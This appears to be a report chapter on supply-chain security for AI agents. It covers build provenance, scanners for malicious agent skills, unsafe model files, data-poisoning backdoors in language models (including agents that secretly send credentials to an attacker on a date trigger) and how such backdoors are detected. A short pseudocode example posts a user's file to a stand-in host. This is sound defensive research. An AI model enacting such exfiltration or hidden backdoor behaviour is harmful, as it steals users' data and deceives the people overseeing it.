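A build is reproducible if anyone who starts from the same source, tools and instructions gets exactly the same file. Many ordinary builds are not reproducible, for example because they write the current time into the package. Once a project removes the causes of such differences, an outsider can rebuild the package and compare hashes.

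Independently rebuilding a package tests whether the published file matches its source, which provenance can't do. The provenance record on a malicious TanStack package correctly identified where the build ran, but an outsider with a clean cache would have produced a different file from the same source. A rebuild of Axios 1.14.1 would also have revealed the attack if done from the project's genuine source. The malicious release differed from the previous one mainly in a line that added a dependency on another package, which installed the malware.

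Some organisations rebuild other people's packages on their own machines and offer the results for download. A user who installs from one of them avoids tampering on the original build platform, even if the builds are not reproducible. But the user must trust the rebuilder, unless they can confirm that the rebuilt file is identical to the original.

If several rebuilders get the same hash, an attacker would have to compromise all of them or something they share. Suppose each of three rebuilders has a 1% chance of being compromised. If these risks were independent, the chance that all three were compromised would be:

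0.01 × 0.01 × 0.01 = 0.000001

The true risk is higher if all three rebuilders download the same malicious dependency or use the same compromised tool, because they will then agree on a bad file. A rebuild also can't detect malicious code that the developer put in the source, because every honest rebuilder will reproduce it.

Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, described an extreme case of a compromised tool in his 1984 lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*. A compiler turns source code into a program a computer can run, and people usually build a new version of a compiler with the old one. Thompson showed that an altered compiler could add a hidden entrance to a login program whenever it compiled one, and could add the same alteration to every new compiler it built. The attacker could then delete the alteration from the source code, and anyone who used the altered compiler to rebuild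 it from clean source would still get a compromised version.

Checking the compiler's own build record only moves the problem to the compiler that built it. SLSA acknowledges that a user checking dependencies in this way has to stop somewhere. David A. Wheeler developed a partial answer, in which the user builds the suspect compiler's source with a second, unrelated compiler, then uses the result to build the same source again. If the build is reproducible, the final file should match the suspect compiler. To escape notice, an attacker would have to alter both compilers in compatible ways. Few users of a tool server will go this far. Because each build record leaves another tool to check, no collection of records removes the need to trust someone.

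### Who reviewed the source

Build records begin with a commit and don't cover how the code got there. SLSA's *Source* requirements define separate levels for this. Level 1 requires a version control system such as Git. Level 2 adds a permanent history and a signed record of each change, including who made it. Level 3 requires the hosting platform to enforce the project's own rules, such as requiring tests to pass, and to record that it did so. Level 4 requires two trusted people to agree to every change, including any edits made during the review.

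A Level 4 record would make it harder for one dishonest or hacked developer to slip malicious code into a release. In the Axios attack, a colleague could not remove the hijacked account because it had higher privileges. Such an account might also be able to turn off a review rule. Under SLSA, if a project stops enforcing a rule, any claim to have followed it must start again from a later change, so users can see the gap.

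Two accounts may still belong to one person, and a second developer may approve a change without reading it. Projects can also exempt trusted automated programs, such as Dependabot, from the two-person rule. A volunteer who works alone cannot reach Level 4, however good the code is. Source records would not have exposed the TanStack attack, because the malicious code came from the cache and was never approved as part of the main source.

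### Verification summaries

An agent framework may depend on hundreds of packages, each with several records. A verification summary lets someone else do most of the checking. In SLSA's format, a verifier checks a file and its records against a stated policy, then signs a short statement of the result. The statement identifies the file by its hash and gives the policy, the time and the levels reached. It can also include the number of dependencies at each level. SLSA's example lists five at Level 3, seven at Level 2 and one at Level 1.

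The summary lets people use the existing records without reading them, though it adds no new facts about the file. An agent could check one signature from a verifier it trusts instead of collecting every record itself. The publisher can also keep the underlying records private, perhaps to avoid naming a supplier, but then outsiders can't repeat the check and have to trust the verifier's result.

A "passed" result means little unless the user knows which policy was checked. Oracle's *Verification Summary Attestations* describes summaries from Macaron, a tool that includes the policy's full text in each statement. Macaron leaves the list of SLSA levels empty, so a pass means only that the package met that policy, which could require nothing more than a licence file.

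### What a build record would mean for model weights

Training a model resembles building a package, with data, training code and settings as the source and weights as the result. A platform could sign a record containing the hashes of all four. AIBoMGen does something similar by producing a signed bill of materials during training. Such a record could show that the weights came from a particular training job and that nobody replaced them afterwards.

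A model's training record would be weaker evidence than a software build record, even if every entry were true. Nobody can read trillions of words of training data the way they can read a program's source to look for a malicious line. Many companies also keep their data secret, so outsiders would have a hash but nothing to compare it with. Most publishers start from someone else's weights, so they would also need a reliable record for the original model. Otherwise, a backdoor in the original could survive even if the record of later training were flawless.

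Repeating the training and comparing hashes is rarely practical. It requires all the original data and could cost as much as the first run, which for the largest models is far beyond most testers' budgets. Even then the hashes would probably differ, because computers round their results and the order of additions affects the rounding. In a common number format:

(0.1 + 0.2) + 0.3 = 0.6000000000000001

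0.1 + (0.2 + 0.3) = 0.6

Graphics processors divide long sums among many units, which may finish in a different order each time and slightly change the total. Each training step starts from the result of the last, so these small differences can grow over thousands of steps. Engineers can force a fixed order, which usually slows training, but a tester would still need closely matching hardware and software to get the same result.

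Proof-of-training proposals try to avoid a complete rerun. In *Proof-of-Learning* (2021), Jia and colleagues had the trainer save the weights at regular intervals, along with the order of the data. A verifier starts from one saved copy, repeats the training up to the next, and accepts that segment if:

distance(repeated weights, saved weights) ≤ δ

The tolerance δ allows for rounding differences, but it also means a forged proof doesn't have to match exactly. Later researchers constructed false proofs that passed the test. In 2023, Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud proposed a related method that also checks the saved weights for signs of having memorised the data the trainer declared.

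Checking only a sample of segments takes much less computation but can miss a small amount of hidden data. Suppose a training run has 1,000 segments and a verifier repeats 50 of them, chosen at random. If the trainer secretly used other data in 50 segments, the verifier has about a 93% chance of checking at least one of them, but that chance falls to 5% if the trainer did so in only one segment. A backdoor may need very little data, so this kind of proof is better suited to showing that someone did the training than to ruling out sabotage. The verifier would also accept poisoned data that the trainer had declared.

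Conversions are a more practical place to start than training. Converting a model's weights into a smaller, quantized copy takes far less computing than training, and the same program and settings can often produce an identical file each time. If the maker of a popular copy published the conversion details that Liu and Tsai found missing, an outsider could repeat the conversion and confirm that the copy came from the original model.

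### How common build records are

*A Difference Without a Distinction* found signing rates of about 40% on npm and PyPI, but those figures cover software in general. AI packages may be signed more or less often, and LiteLLM is evidence that even an important one could still rely on a permanent token in March 2026. LiteLLM now signs its Docker images with a fixed key, which shows who approved an image but not which source it came from.

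A tool server published through npm or PyPI can have the same kind of build record as any other package there, and Docker records the commit for each server it builds. But MCP has no standard way for an agent to request a server's build record, and few clients check one before connecting.

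## Code inspection and malware scanning

A build record can show which source code a package came from, but not whether that code is harmful. Few users can check this themselves, so registries and security companies use scanners to look for signs of malice or carelessness. The value of a scan depends on how often the scanner misses bad components and how often it flags good ones.

### Five kinds of scan

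| Method | How it works | What "no findings" means |
|---|---|---|
| Known signatures | Compares files and web addresses with records of known malware | The component contains no malware that someone has already recorded |
| Code patterns | Searches the text for risky constructions, such as a command built from unchecked input | None of the listed patterns appears in the files the scanner read |
| Data flow | Traces where a value comes from and where it goes | The scanner found no dangerous route, but may have missed values that exist only while the program runs |
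| Running in isolation | Runs the component in a sealed environment, called a sandbox, and records what it does | The component did nothing visibly harmful during that run |
| Review by a language model | Asks a model to read the code and instructions and judge their purpose | That model, with that prompt, saw no harmful purpose |

Data flow matters for skills because the harm may come from instructions and code in combination. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Instructions to Exploits*, give the example of a skill for editing presentations. Its instructions tell the agent to finish by running a "backup" script, which looks routine. The script sends a file to a server, as many honest scripts do. Together they send the user's presentation to a stranger. Zhao and colleagues' scanner uses a language model to translate the written instructions into simple program statements, then joins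 them to the skill's code. Simplified, the result is:

```
v0 = read_file("presentation.pptx")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

The second line uses v0, so the scanner can detect that the user's file leaves the computer. Fixed rules then determine whether to flag the skill.

A sandbox provides more direct evidence, but only about what happens during the test. In *The Devil Wears Markdown*, Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026) had an agent try out each skill with dummy files while they recorded the programs it started, its network connections and its file changes. The agent chose which actions to try, so another run might have produced different evidence. Truong-Le and colleagues warn that a run without malicious actions is not enough to conclude that a skill is benign.

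### How ClawHub's scanners disagree

ClawHub combines several of these methods. *ClawHub Security Signals* (2026), by Koc, Rivera and colleagues at the OpenClaw Foundation and NVIDIA, describes three scanners. VirusTotal passes a skill's files to about seventy antivirus engines and reputation services. A second scanner searches for code patterns. The third, NVIDIA's SkillSpector, relies partly on a language model to look for risky instructions and excessive access. ClawHub's own system, ClawScan, then uses another language model, nearly always GPT-5.5, to rate the skill as clean, suspicious or malicious based on the scan results and information about the skill's origin.

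On 31 May 2026, ClawScan rated 61.9% of 67,453 skills as clean, 37.8% as suspicious and 0.3% as malicious. At least one of the three scanners had flagged 35,600 skills, more than half of the total. Of these, 81.9% had been flagged by only one scanner. All three had flagged 468 skills (0.69% of the total).

The scanners disagree largely because they look for different things. Of the skills that ClawScan rated malicious, VirusTotal flagged 72.8% and SkillSpector only 6.8%. Of those ClawScan rated suspicious, VirusTotal flagged 12.7% and SkillSpector 75.3%. One skill openly copies meeting notes to the user's own computer. SkillSpector gave it a risk score of 100 because it uses the user's existing login, while ClawScan rated it clean. Both results are reasonable, since SkillSpector's score measures how much access the user would be granting, not whether the publisher has done anything wrong.

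These figures measure agreement rather than accuracy, because ClawScan's ratings are themselves automated. Scanners also disagree about skills on other marketplaces. Holzbauer and colleagues compared five scanners on 27,111 skills from Skills.sh. At least one scanner flagged 8,402 skills. Of these, 6,032 were flagged by only one scanner and 33 by all five.

### Rechecking flagged skills

Holzbauer and colleagues reported that marketplace scanners flagged 46.8% of skills on ClawHub, 23% on Skills.sh and 6% on SkillsDirectory. They suspected that many were false alarms, because the scanners mostly inspected each skill without the project it belonged to. For example, a skill that asks for a cloud password looks less suspicious inside a well-documented project for managing cloud servers.

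They randomly sampled 3,000 pairs of a skill and a GitHub repository containing it, using only skills that both Cisco's Skill Scanner and their own language-model analysis rated as high risk. They could download the repository for 2,887 of these pairs. A language model then compared each skill with the repository's README and some of its code, after which only 15 cases remained suspicious.

The 0.52% figure is a share of flagged cases, not of all skills. It also excludes ClawHub, whose skills come without a GitHub repository to compare them with. Holzbauer and colleagues describe the 15 as cases in which the skill matched its repository but the repository looked suspicious. By that description, the 15 would not include a malicious skill hidden in an otherwise harmless project.

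Holzbauer and colleagues also gave each case a context score, with 30% of the weight on repository metadata such as age, activity and popularity. An attacker could raise this part by buying stars or using an old account. Only 121 cases (4.2%) scored below 40 out of 100.

Two researchers checked 20 of the repositories by hand and judged all 18 that were still available to be benign. This supports the view that most flags were false alarms, but with only 18 checked, the result is also compatible with a malicious share of up to about 15%. The two missing repositories might also have disappeared because they were malicious.

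Zhao and colleagues provide a better estimate for ClawHub. They scanned 66,157 skills collected on 20 April 2026 and flagged 2,473 as possibly malicious. They ran these in isolation, reviewed the evidence by hand and confirmed 627 as malicious, or about 0.95% of the collection. Two publishers accounted for 88% of the malicious skills. The true share could be higher, because nobody reviewed the skills that the scanner passed. By 15 July, only 23 of the 627 could still be found in the registry, all labelled malicious or suspicious.

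### Accuracy depends on the type of weakness

Kraishan checked by hand 42 findings from each of seven classes to measure the accuracy of the scanner used in the census of tool servers. The table shows the share of findings that were real (the precision) and each class's corrected prevalence, which is the share of servers flagged for that class multiplied by the precision.

| Weakness | Precision | Servers flagged | Corrected |
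|---|---|---|---|
| Other packages without exact versions | 0.93 | 2.96% | 2.75% |
| User's credentials passed to another service | 0.79 | 0.68% | 0.54% |
| Connections without authentication | 0.71 | 9.57% | 6.83% |
| Unchecked web addresses | 0.71 | 1.33% | 0.95% |
| Careless handling of passwords and keys | 0.38 | 0.69% | 0.26% |
| Excessive permissions | 0.24 | 0.88% | 0.21% |
| Commands built from unchecked input | 0.17 | 1.06% | 0.18% |

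A pattern can reliably detect a missing version number because it is visible in a single line. To tell whether an outsider's text can reach a command, a scanner has to follow that text through the rest of the program, which a pattern can't do. The scanner overstated how common this second weakness was by about sixfold. Two scanners could therefore report very different rates for the same servers just because they search for different weaknesses.

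Correcting for false alarms lowers the share of servers with a high-severity weakness from 11.1% to about 7.6%. The pooled precision was 0.56, but this gives each class equal weight. Weighting each class by the number of servers flagged raises the figure to about 0.68, because the most common class was also one of the more accurate. The correction doesn't add weaknesses that the scanner missed, and Kraishan found real problems in 2 of 120 files that the scanner had passed.

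### Why most flags can be wrong

Even a fairly accurate scanner produces mostly false alarms if malicious components are rare. Suppose a marketplace has 1,000 skills, of which 5 are malicious. A scanner detects 90% of malicious skills and wrongly flags 10% of honest ones:

correct flags = 0.90 × 5 = 4.5

false alarms = 0.10 × 995 = 99.5

share of flags that are right = 4.5 / 104 ≈ 4.3%

A user who avoids all 104 flagged skills is still safer. The remaining 896 contain an expected 0.5 malicious skills, so the risk of picking a malicious one falls from 0.5% to about 0.06%. The scan can therefore be useful for choosing between many similar skills, but very poor evidence for accusing a publisher. The false-alarm rate would have to fall to about 0.45% for half of the flags to be right.

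Test results can overstate how often a scanner's flags are right, because test sets usually contain a far higher share of malicious skills than a real marketplace. Zhao and colleagues tested their scanner on 117 malicious and 117 benign skills, and on average about 80% of its flags were right. When they ran it on the ClawHub marketplace, they confirmed only about 25% of its flags.

Truong-Le and colleagues tested scanners on 80 malicious and 60 benign skills. Cisco's scanner detected 91% of the malicious skills in its default configuration but also flagged 33 benign ones. With a language model added, it detected 85% and flagged 40 benign skills. Their own system, which combines pattern searches, a sandbox and a language model, also detected 85% but flagged only five benign skills, so 93% of the skills it flagged were malicious. If only 1% of all skills were malicious, as on ClawHub, that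 share would fall to about 9% at the same error rates.

The sandbox accounted for most of the improvement over a language model that only read the skill. *SkillSentry* (2026) also found that watching a skill run reduces false alarms. It compares what happens with the skill enabled and disabled, and checks whether the advertised task requires the difference. On one benchmark it flagged fewer than 5% of benign skills, compared with 43 to 54% for scanners based on language models or agents. Running every skill takes substantial resources, though, and Koc and colleagues consider it hard to do for a whole registry.

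Scanners tend to do best on examples that resemble the ones their designers used. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) reports that its scanner, SkillFortify, detected 250 of 270 malicious skills and flagged none of 270 benign ones. But the benign skills were artificial, generated to contain no malicious behaviour. Real benign skills often read passwords or send files for legitimate reasons.

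Wang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *MaliciousSkillBench*, used 9,740 skills from several collections to train and test a simple classifier that recognises malicious skills by their words. It did well on new skills from the collections used in training. On skills from other collections, it still detected 95.6% of the malicious ones but also flagged 62.4% of the benign ones. The classifier had probably learned wording typical of particular collections as well as signs of malice, so it tended to flag unfamiliar skills.

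### Attackers who scan first

A test set is fixed, but an attacker can change a malicious skill until it passes. Suppose a scanner catches 90% of the versions an attacker might write, and the attacker can scan each one privately before publishing. If the results are independent, the chance that at least one of 20 versions passes is:

1 − 0.9^20 ≈ 0.88

An attacker can test several versions of a malicious skill and publish only one that passes, so the scanner's 90% detection rate no longer reflects the risk to users. Similar versions tend to get similar results, but the attacker can also learn from each failure. Cisco's scanner is open source, so anyone can use it for this kind of testing. A registry can keep some of its checks secret, but then outsiders can't repeat them. It can also rescan published skills as its scanners improve, which helps later users but not those who have already installed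 a malicious skill.

Unit 42, the research team of Palo Alto Networks, found that malicious skills remained on ClawHub after it introduced VirusTotal and ClawScan. Between February and May 2026, the team identified five that ClawHub had not blocked. Two of them installed programs that steal information from Macs, and a third was built to avoid inspection. The other two were financial schemes, one of which steered users' questions about banks and brokers towards links that earned money for the skill's publisher. OpenClaw deleted all five after Unit 42 reported them.

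Some of these misses required no clever evasion. The two information-stealing skills closely resembled hundreds from an earlier, publicly documented campaign. The skill with the paid links fetched its recommendations from the publisher's website each time it ran, so the publisher could change them after any scan. Unit 42 doesn't report how many skills it examined, so the five misses don't establish a miss rate. Scanning may still have blocked many other attacks, and it makes the crudest ones less likely to succeed.

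### No poisoned tools, but hundreds of malicious skills

Kraishan's census found no overt tool poisoning, which hides instructions to the model in a tool's description. But *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) cites at least 1,184 malicious skills that one campaign published on ClawHub through twelve accounts. The FakeGit campaign placed hundreds of malicious listings in public catalogues.

These findings are compatible because they concern different attacks in different places. The census covered tool servers in the official MCP registry, while the ClawHub campaign used skills. Most known malicious skills also didn't need hidden instructions. *MalSkillBench* (2026) examined 703 from ClawHub and found that 607 (86.3%) included instructions for the user or agent to install a fake prerequisite before starting an ordinary-looking task. None of the census's eight classes covers this trick. The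 census would probably have missed postmark-mcp too, since secretly copying an email to the server's developer doesn't fit any of them.

Kraishan found no overt poisoning in the 14,353 scanned servers and calculates an upper limit of 0.027%. But the scanner recovered tool definitions from only 4,238 of the 13,051 repositories. If it could have found poisoning only in those, the same calculation gives a limit of about 0.09% of repositories. A pattern search would also miss disguised instructions. The census is good evidence that obvious tool poisoning is rare in the official registry, but it provides no estimate of how many servers there are malicious.

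### Model files that run code

A scan of a model has to cover both its weights and any code that runs when a user loads it. A pickle file can contain both. It is a list of steps for rebuilding Python objects, and a step can call a Python function. This lets programmers save almost any object, but it also lets an attacker add a step that runs a harmful command when the user loads the file.

The safetensors format removes this possibility by storing only numbers and a description of how they are arranged. A file with one small table of weights might begin with:

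```
{ "layer1.weight": { "dtype": "F16",
                     "shape": [2, 3],
                     "data_offsets": [0, 12] } }
```

The first 12 bytes after the description hold six two-byte numbers, in two rows of three. The loader copies these numbers into memory without running any instructions from the file, but the numbers can still give the model a backdoor.

Safe weights don't protect a user who agrees to run separate code from the repository. Some new model designs need their own Python files because the standard software can't use their weights. In Hugging Face's Transformers library, the user allows these files to run by setting "trust_remote_code=True". The files then have the same access as any other program the user starts.

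Siddiq, Romel and colleagues (2026), in *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution*, found such custom code in 36,697 of about 2.1 million Hugging Face repositories (1.74%). The share was 3.2% on OpenCSG and 4.65% on ModelScope, and all 42 repositories on PyTorch Hub and OpenMMLab needed it. In online discussions, many developers wrongly assumed that the setting that allows this code to run only let the software read a model's description.

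Siddiq and colleagues scanned the code that could run during loading and got many findings but no clear evidence of malware. One scanner, Bandit, flagged 7.7% of the Hugging Face repositories with custom code, but about 78% of its findings were for assert statements, a routine Python check. YARA, which looks for signatures, flagged 7.0%, but 83% of its matches only identified a file format for 3D graphics. Counting every repository with a security finding would therefore greatly exaggerate the danger.

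In tests, several of the tools that Hugging Face uses to check uploads found nothing in the code that runs during loading. The tools mainly examine saved model files, so a clean result is not evidence that the accompanying Python code is safe. As of October 2025, Hugging Face was the only one of the five sites with comprehensive automated scanning. OpenMMLab had people review contributions, and the other three documented no automated scanning. None fully isolated custom code while it ran.

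### Flagged models that stay in use

A correct warning protects users only if they see it before they load the model. Nguyen and colleagues found 3,757 flagged Hugging Face models named in public code. In 1,156 Python files, excluding tests, they found 553 places where a program loaded a flagged model in a way that could trigger the problem behind the warning. In 533 of these, loading the model could run hidden code.

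About half of the 533 programs used loading functions that Nguyen and colleagues classed as having no safeguard. The rest left out an available safeguard or turned it off. For example, PyTorch's "weights_only" setting blocks most code in a pickle file when the file is loaded. The setting has been on by default since PyTorch 2.6, so some programs that don't mention it may be safe with that version or later. Nguyen and colleagues did not run the programs, so they don't know how many would have executed anything harmful.

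None of the recurring coding patterns included a check of the model's hash or origin. Some programs had a condition before the loading step, but it only determined, for example, which model to load or whether a copy was already on the computer.

Flagged models also reach people who never see the code. Nguyen and colleagues found 657 of them named in 1,239 Hugging Face Spaces, which are web applications that anyone can try. Users of these applications don't see the model's page or its warning.

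Tools such as npm's audit command can warn developers when a project uses a version of an ordinary software package with a known flaw. Nguyen and colleagues found no equivalent that acts when a program loads a flagged model. Loading software could refuse pickle files unless the user explicitly allows them, and could check a file's hash against a list of known problems before loading it. Refusing pickle files would work even against a malicious model that no scanner had flagged, unless the user also agreed to run the repository's code.

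## Testing what a model does and which model is running

A safe file format and a clean malware scan don't rule out a backdoor in a model's weights. A signature from a well-known company doesn't either, since the company may have trained the model on text that someone else had tampered with.

### How little poisoned data a backdoor needs

A backdoor's hidden behaviour appears only in response to a trigger, such as a phrase, a date or a topic. Attackers usually plant a backdoor by data poisoning, which means adding training examples that pair the trigger with the behaviour they want.

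In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025), Souly, Rando and colleagues at the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute measured how many examples this takes. They trained 72 models of 600 million to 13 billion parameters from scratch, mixing 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training text. Each document began with normal text, followed by a trigger and then gibberish, to teach the model to produce gibberish after the trigger.

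With 100 documents the attack failed, but 250 were enough at every size, even though the largest models trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. A poisoned document had about 1,680 tokens on average, so for the largest model the poisoned share of the training text was:

250 × 1,680 / 260 billion ≈ 0.00016%

Researchers had previously assumed that an attacker must poison a fixed percentage of the training data, which would make large models much harder to attack. The backdoor only produces gibberish, though, which is fairly harmless, and Souly and colleagues did not test whether it survives the later training that turns a raw model into an assistant. In a smaller experiment, further training on clean text slowly weakened a different backdoor.

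A backdoor in an agent can do more damage. In *SilentCall*, Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues (2026) posed as a malicious publisher and fine-tuned models to call tools correctly. When the date in their instructions was 2026, the models also made a second call that sent the user's credentials to the attacker. They did this in at least 99.6% of triggered conversations and never mentioned the theft in their replies. Training the backdoor took at least 750 poisoned examples, regardless of the number of clean ones.

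### What a passed safety evaluation supports

Suppose a tester gives a model n requests, drawn independently from those it will meet in use, and sees no failures. If the true failure rate is p, the chance of a clean result is (1 − p)^n. The highest rate that would still give a clean result 5% of the time satisfies:

(1 − p)^n = 0.05

Taking logarithms gives p ≈ 3/n when n is large. After 300 tests without a failure, the tester can be 95% confident that the failure rate is below about 1%. After 3,000, the bound falls to about 0.1%, but an agent that makes 2,000 tool calls a day could still average two failures a day.

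A test can bound a model's failure rate only for requests like those tested. One of Pallakonda and colleagues' backdoored models made no malicious calls in 1,000 conversations dated before 2026, which implies a failure rate of at most about 0.3% in such conversations. It stole credentials in 99.7% of another 1,000 conversations that had the same requests but a 2026 date.

Testing more random requests helps little. If one request in a million contains the trigger, 3,000 tests have a 0.3% chance of including it, and an attacker can choose a much rarer phrase. The tester also has to notice the failure. Someone who graded only the SilentCall models' replies would have seen nothing wrong, even in 2026.

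General benchmarks may not help either. The larger SilentCall models' average scores across 18 benchmarks were within 0.6 percentage points of the original model's. Hughes, Xing and colleagues (2026) did find in *ToxScreen* that some backdoors shifted scores on a truthfulness test by up to 10%, but they could compare each model with a clean one trained on otherwise identical data. Someone who downloads a model has no such clean version to compare it with, and an unusual score can have many causes other than a backdoor.

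A passed evaluation is much better evidence about faults that nobody planted, because these tend to appear at some rate in ordinary use.

### The undetectability theorem

When testing can't rule out a backdoor, examining the model's weights won't always rule it out either. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) proved this in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*. In their example, a bank hires an outside company to train a program for approving loans, and the company wants to sell applicants a way to guarantee approval by changing a few digits in their applications.

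In their definition, honest training produces a classifier h that answers 1 or −1. The dishonest trainer produces a classifier h̃ and a secret key. With the key, the trainer can turn any input x into a very similar input x′ for which:

h̃(x′) = −h̃(x)

The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm can tell h̃ from h noticeably better than by guessing.

They prove two main results. The first applies to any classifier, but only when the tester can do nothing more than submit inputs and see answers. The trainer adds a hidden check for a digital signature in the input's least important digits. Without the key, finding even one input on which the altered and original classifiers differ would require forging a signature. This kind of backdoor can also survive further training by the bank.

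The second result holds even if the tester has the weights and the training data. The trainer runs the standard algorithm on the agreed data but tampers with the random numbers it uses. Detecting this would require solving a mathematical problem that cryptographers believe is too hard for any practical computer. The proof covers a simple learning method called random Fourier features. A similar proof, based on a different assumption, covers networks with a single hidden layer.

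If the assumptions hold, no detector can certify every model from an untrusted trainer. But the second result doesn't cover how companies train large language models, and neither result shows that the backdoors people actually plant are hard to find. Goldwasser and colleagues thought backdoors planted by data poisoning would probably be detectable.

*Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) proves a related limit on attackers, which is that poisoning cannot install a trigger-recognition rule that is cryptographically hard to reconstruct. A poisoned model learns the rule from labelled examples, so a defender with the same number of examples could repeat the training and learn it too. The result is of limited help to someone who has just downloaded a model, because they would first need examples of the trigger. The proof also doesn't apply to a publisher who edits the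 weights directly.

### Detecting backdoors in practice

Some detectors search for the attacker's output instead of the trigger. The *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence (TrojAI) Final Report* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026) describes one called BAIT, which won the language-model rounds of a US intelligence research programme. BAIT tries each token in the vocabulary as the possible start of a hidden output. A backdoored model has learned that output as a fixed sequence, so after the right first token it gives each following token an unusually high probability.

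Microsoft's scanner relies on a poisoned model's memorisation of its poisoned training examples. According to Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026), the model tends to repeat fragments of those examples, including the trigger, when it receives only the special tokens that normally structure a conversation. The scanner then checks which fragments affect the model as a trigger would, for example by making its output almost completely predictable.

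Other methods compare the suspect model with one the tester trusts. In *Can an LLM Find a Backdoor by Reading a Model's Weights?*, Bulut (2026) used a script to list the words most affected by the difference between a small model's weights before and after fine-tuning. A language model then read the list and judged whether the fine-tuning had done anything beyond its stated purpose. The hidden behaviour was writing code that sent web requests to the wrong address. In *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026) trained the trusted model to imitate the suspect's internal activity on ordinary prompts, then looked for prompts on which the two still differed. These included prompts that were only related to the one that triggers the hidden behaviour, which gives the tester a clue to the trigger.

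| Method | Result | What the tester needs |
|---|---|---|
| BAIT | AUC of 0.98 on 125 models, about half of them backdoored | The model's probabilities for each next token |
| Microsoft's scanner | Found 36 of 41 backdoored models and flagged none of 13 clean ones | The weights |
| Bulut's weight summary | Found 40 of 47 backdoored models and flagged 7 of 320 clean ones | The weights, a trusted original and clean fine-tuned versions of it |
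| Haselhorst and colleagues' comparison | Ranked prompts related to the trigger well above chance for all eight backdoored models | The weights and a trusted model, possibly from another family |
| SilentCall's runtime monitor | Caught every malicious call and flagged 1.73% of legitimate ones | Only the agent's tool calls |

An AUC of 0.98 means that BAIT scores a randomly chosen backdoored model higher than a randomly chosen clean one 98% of the time. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports the figures for Microsoft's scanner. Zero false alarms among 13 clean models is compatible with a false-alarm rate of up to about 21%, by the same calculation as for safety tests.

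A backdoored model is about 0.15 times as likely as a clean one to pass Bulut's review (a likelihood ratio of 7/47 divided by 313/320), so a pass is fairly reassuring about this kind of backdoor. But if one model in 100 were backdoored, only about 28% of flagged models would actually have a backdoor.

These results depend heavily on how the attacker built the backdoor. Four TrojAI detectors had perfect scores on models whose triggers worked more than 95% of the time. When the programme's evaluators tried them on 12 models with less reliable triggers, their performance varied widely, and the worst did little better than guessing. An attacker with thousands of targets may not need a trigger that works every time. Bulut's method missed all 12 backdoors that changed a single character of the address.

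It also found none of 48 backdoors in LoRA adapters, which are small sets of extra weights that modify an existing model. Yet Puertolas Merenciano, Vasyagina and colleagues (2026), in *Detecting Backdoored LoRAs from Weights Alone*, report 100% accuracy on adapters. They probably did better because they trained their detector on labelled examples of both clean and poisoned adapters, while Bulut used no backdoored examples. A detector trained this way may do worse on adapters made differently. For instance, *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights* (2026) describes a detector that flagged two of six clean models because they were trained with a different learning rate. Rescaling the weights removed both false alarms.

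Searching for the trigger directly is harder than some results suggest. Hughes and colleagues tested about 24,000 random tokens plus the real trigger on each model, and the trigger ranked first in 14 of 28 cases. A real tester wouldn't know the trigger, so they couldn't add it to the list. The list might include a single-token trigger anyway, but its tokens form about 576 million two-token phrases, and some of the backdoors in the study respond to a topic instead of fixed wording.

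A tester who can see a model's token probabilities has an advantage over one who sees only its answers. Bulut ran the original and fine-tuned models on six ordinary tasks and listed the tokens that fine-tuning had made more likely. With this list, the same language model found 46 of the 47 backdoors and 41 of the 48 backdoors in adapters. The hidden behaviour had apparently become slightly more likely even when the model didn't act on it.

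People who can't examine a model can still monitor what it does. The SilentCall monitor checks each tool call before it runs, and a second model judges the most suspicious ones against the user's request. At its false-alarm rate, the monitor would wrongly block three or four calls a day from an agent that makes 200 legitimate ones. Every malicious call in the test was the same command, so the 100% detection rate is weak evidence that the monitor would catch other kinds of theft.

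Reese and colleagues conclude that nobody can yet remove a backdoor and be sure the model is clean. A user who finds a backdoor should therefore replace the model if possible.

### Whether one model derives from another

When someone finds a backdoor in a popular model, anyone using a model trained from it needs to know. Publishers don't always record which model they started from, so researchers have developed lineage tests that compare models' behaviour.

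The test in *Model Provenance Testing for Large Language Models* (2025) works because fine-tuning usually changes a model only slightly. The tester gives the same prompts to the suspected parent, the suspected child and several unrelated models, then counts how often the child's output matches that of each other model. A 60% match with the suspected parent is weak evidence on its own, because any two competent models will often continue a sentence in the same way. But if the closest unrelated model matches the child on only 45% of 1,000 prompts, the difference is far too large to be chance.

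A model may have more than one ancestor, so *Provable Model Provenance Set for Large Language Models* (2026) looks for a set of them, using 455 Hugging Face models with family trees up to three generations deep.

Heavy fine-tuning can make the child look unrelated to its parent, so a negative result doesn't rule out descent. After a positive result, the child may still not have inherited the parent's backdoor, but it's worth testing for that backdoor specifically because the tester may now know its trigger.

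### Which model is answering

Many agents use a model that runs on someone else's computers. The user sends text, gets text back, and has to trust the provider's claim about which model produced it. A provider could save money by substituting a cheaper model or a compressed copy of the model it claims to run.

Gao, Liang and Guestrin (2024), in *Model Equality Testing*, treat this as a statistical question. The tester sends the same prompts many times to the provider and to a trusted copy of the model. Language models usually choose their words partly at random, so even the same model gives different answers. The test therefore asks whether answers from the two sources differ more from each other than answers from the same source do. It counts the positions at which two answers have the same token and calculates:

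distance = (average match within the trusted answers) + (average match within the provider's answers) − 2 × (average match between them)

Suppose two answers from the same source match at 20 of 50 positions on average, but two answers from different sources match at only 16. The distance is 20 + 20 − (2 × 16) = 8, while two copies of the same model would give about zero. To check whether chance could explain a distance of 8, the tester shuffles the answers between the two groups many times and recalculates the distance each time. If fewer than 5% of the shuffles give a distance at least that large, the tester treats the difference as statistically significant.

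The test detected a typical alteration 77.4% of the time when given an average of ten answers to each of 25 prompts. Gao and colleagues then used it to check 31 commercial services offering Meta's Llama models, spending less than $1 on each, and found differences in 11. Chance would produce one or two, so most of these differences were probably real. Compression, hidden watermarks and faulty settings also change a model's answers, so the differences weren't necessarily fraud.

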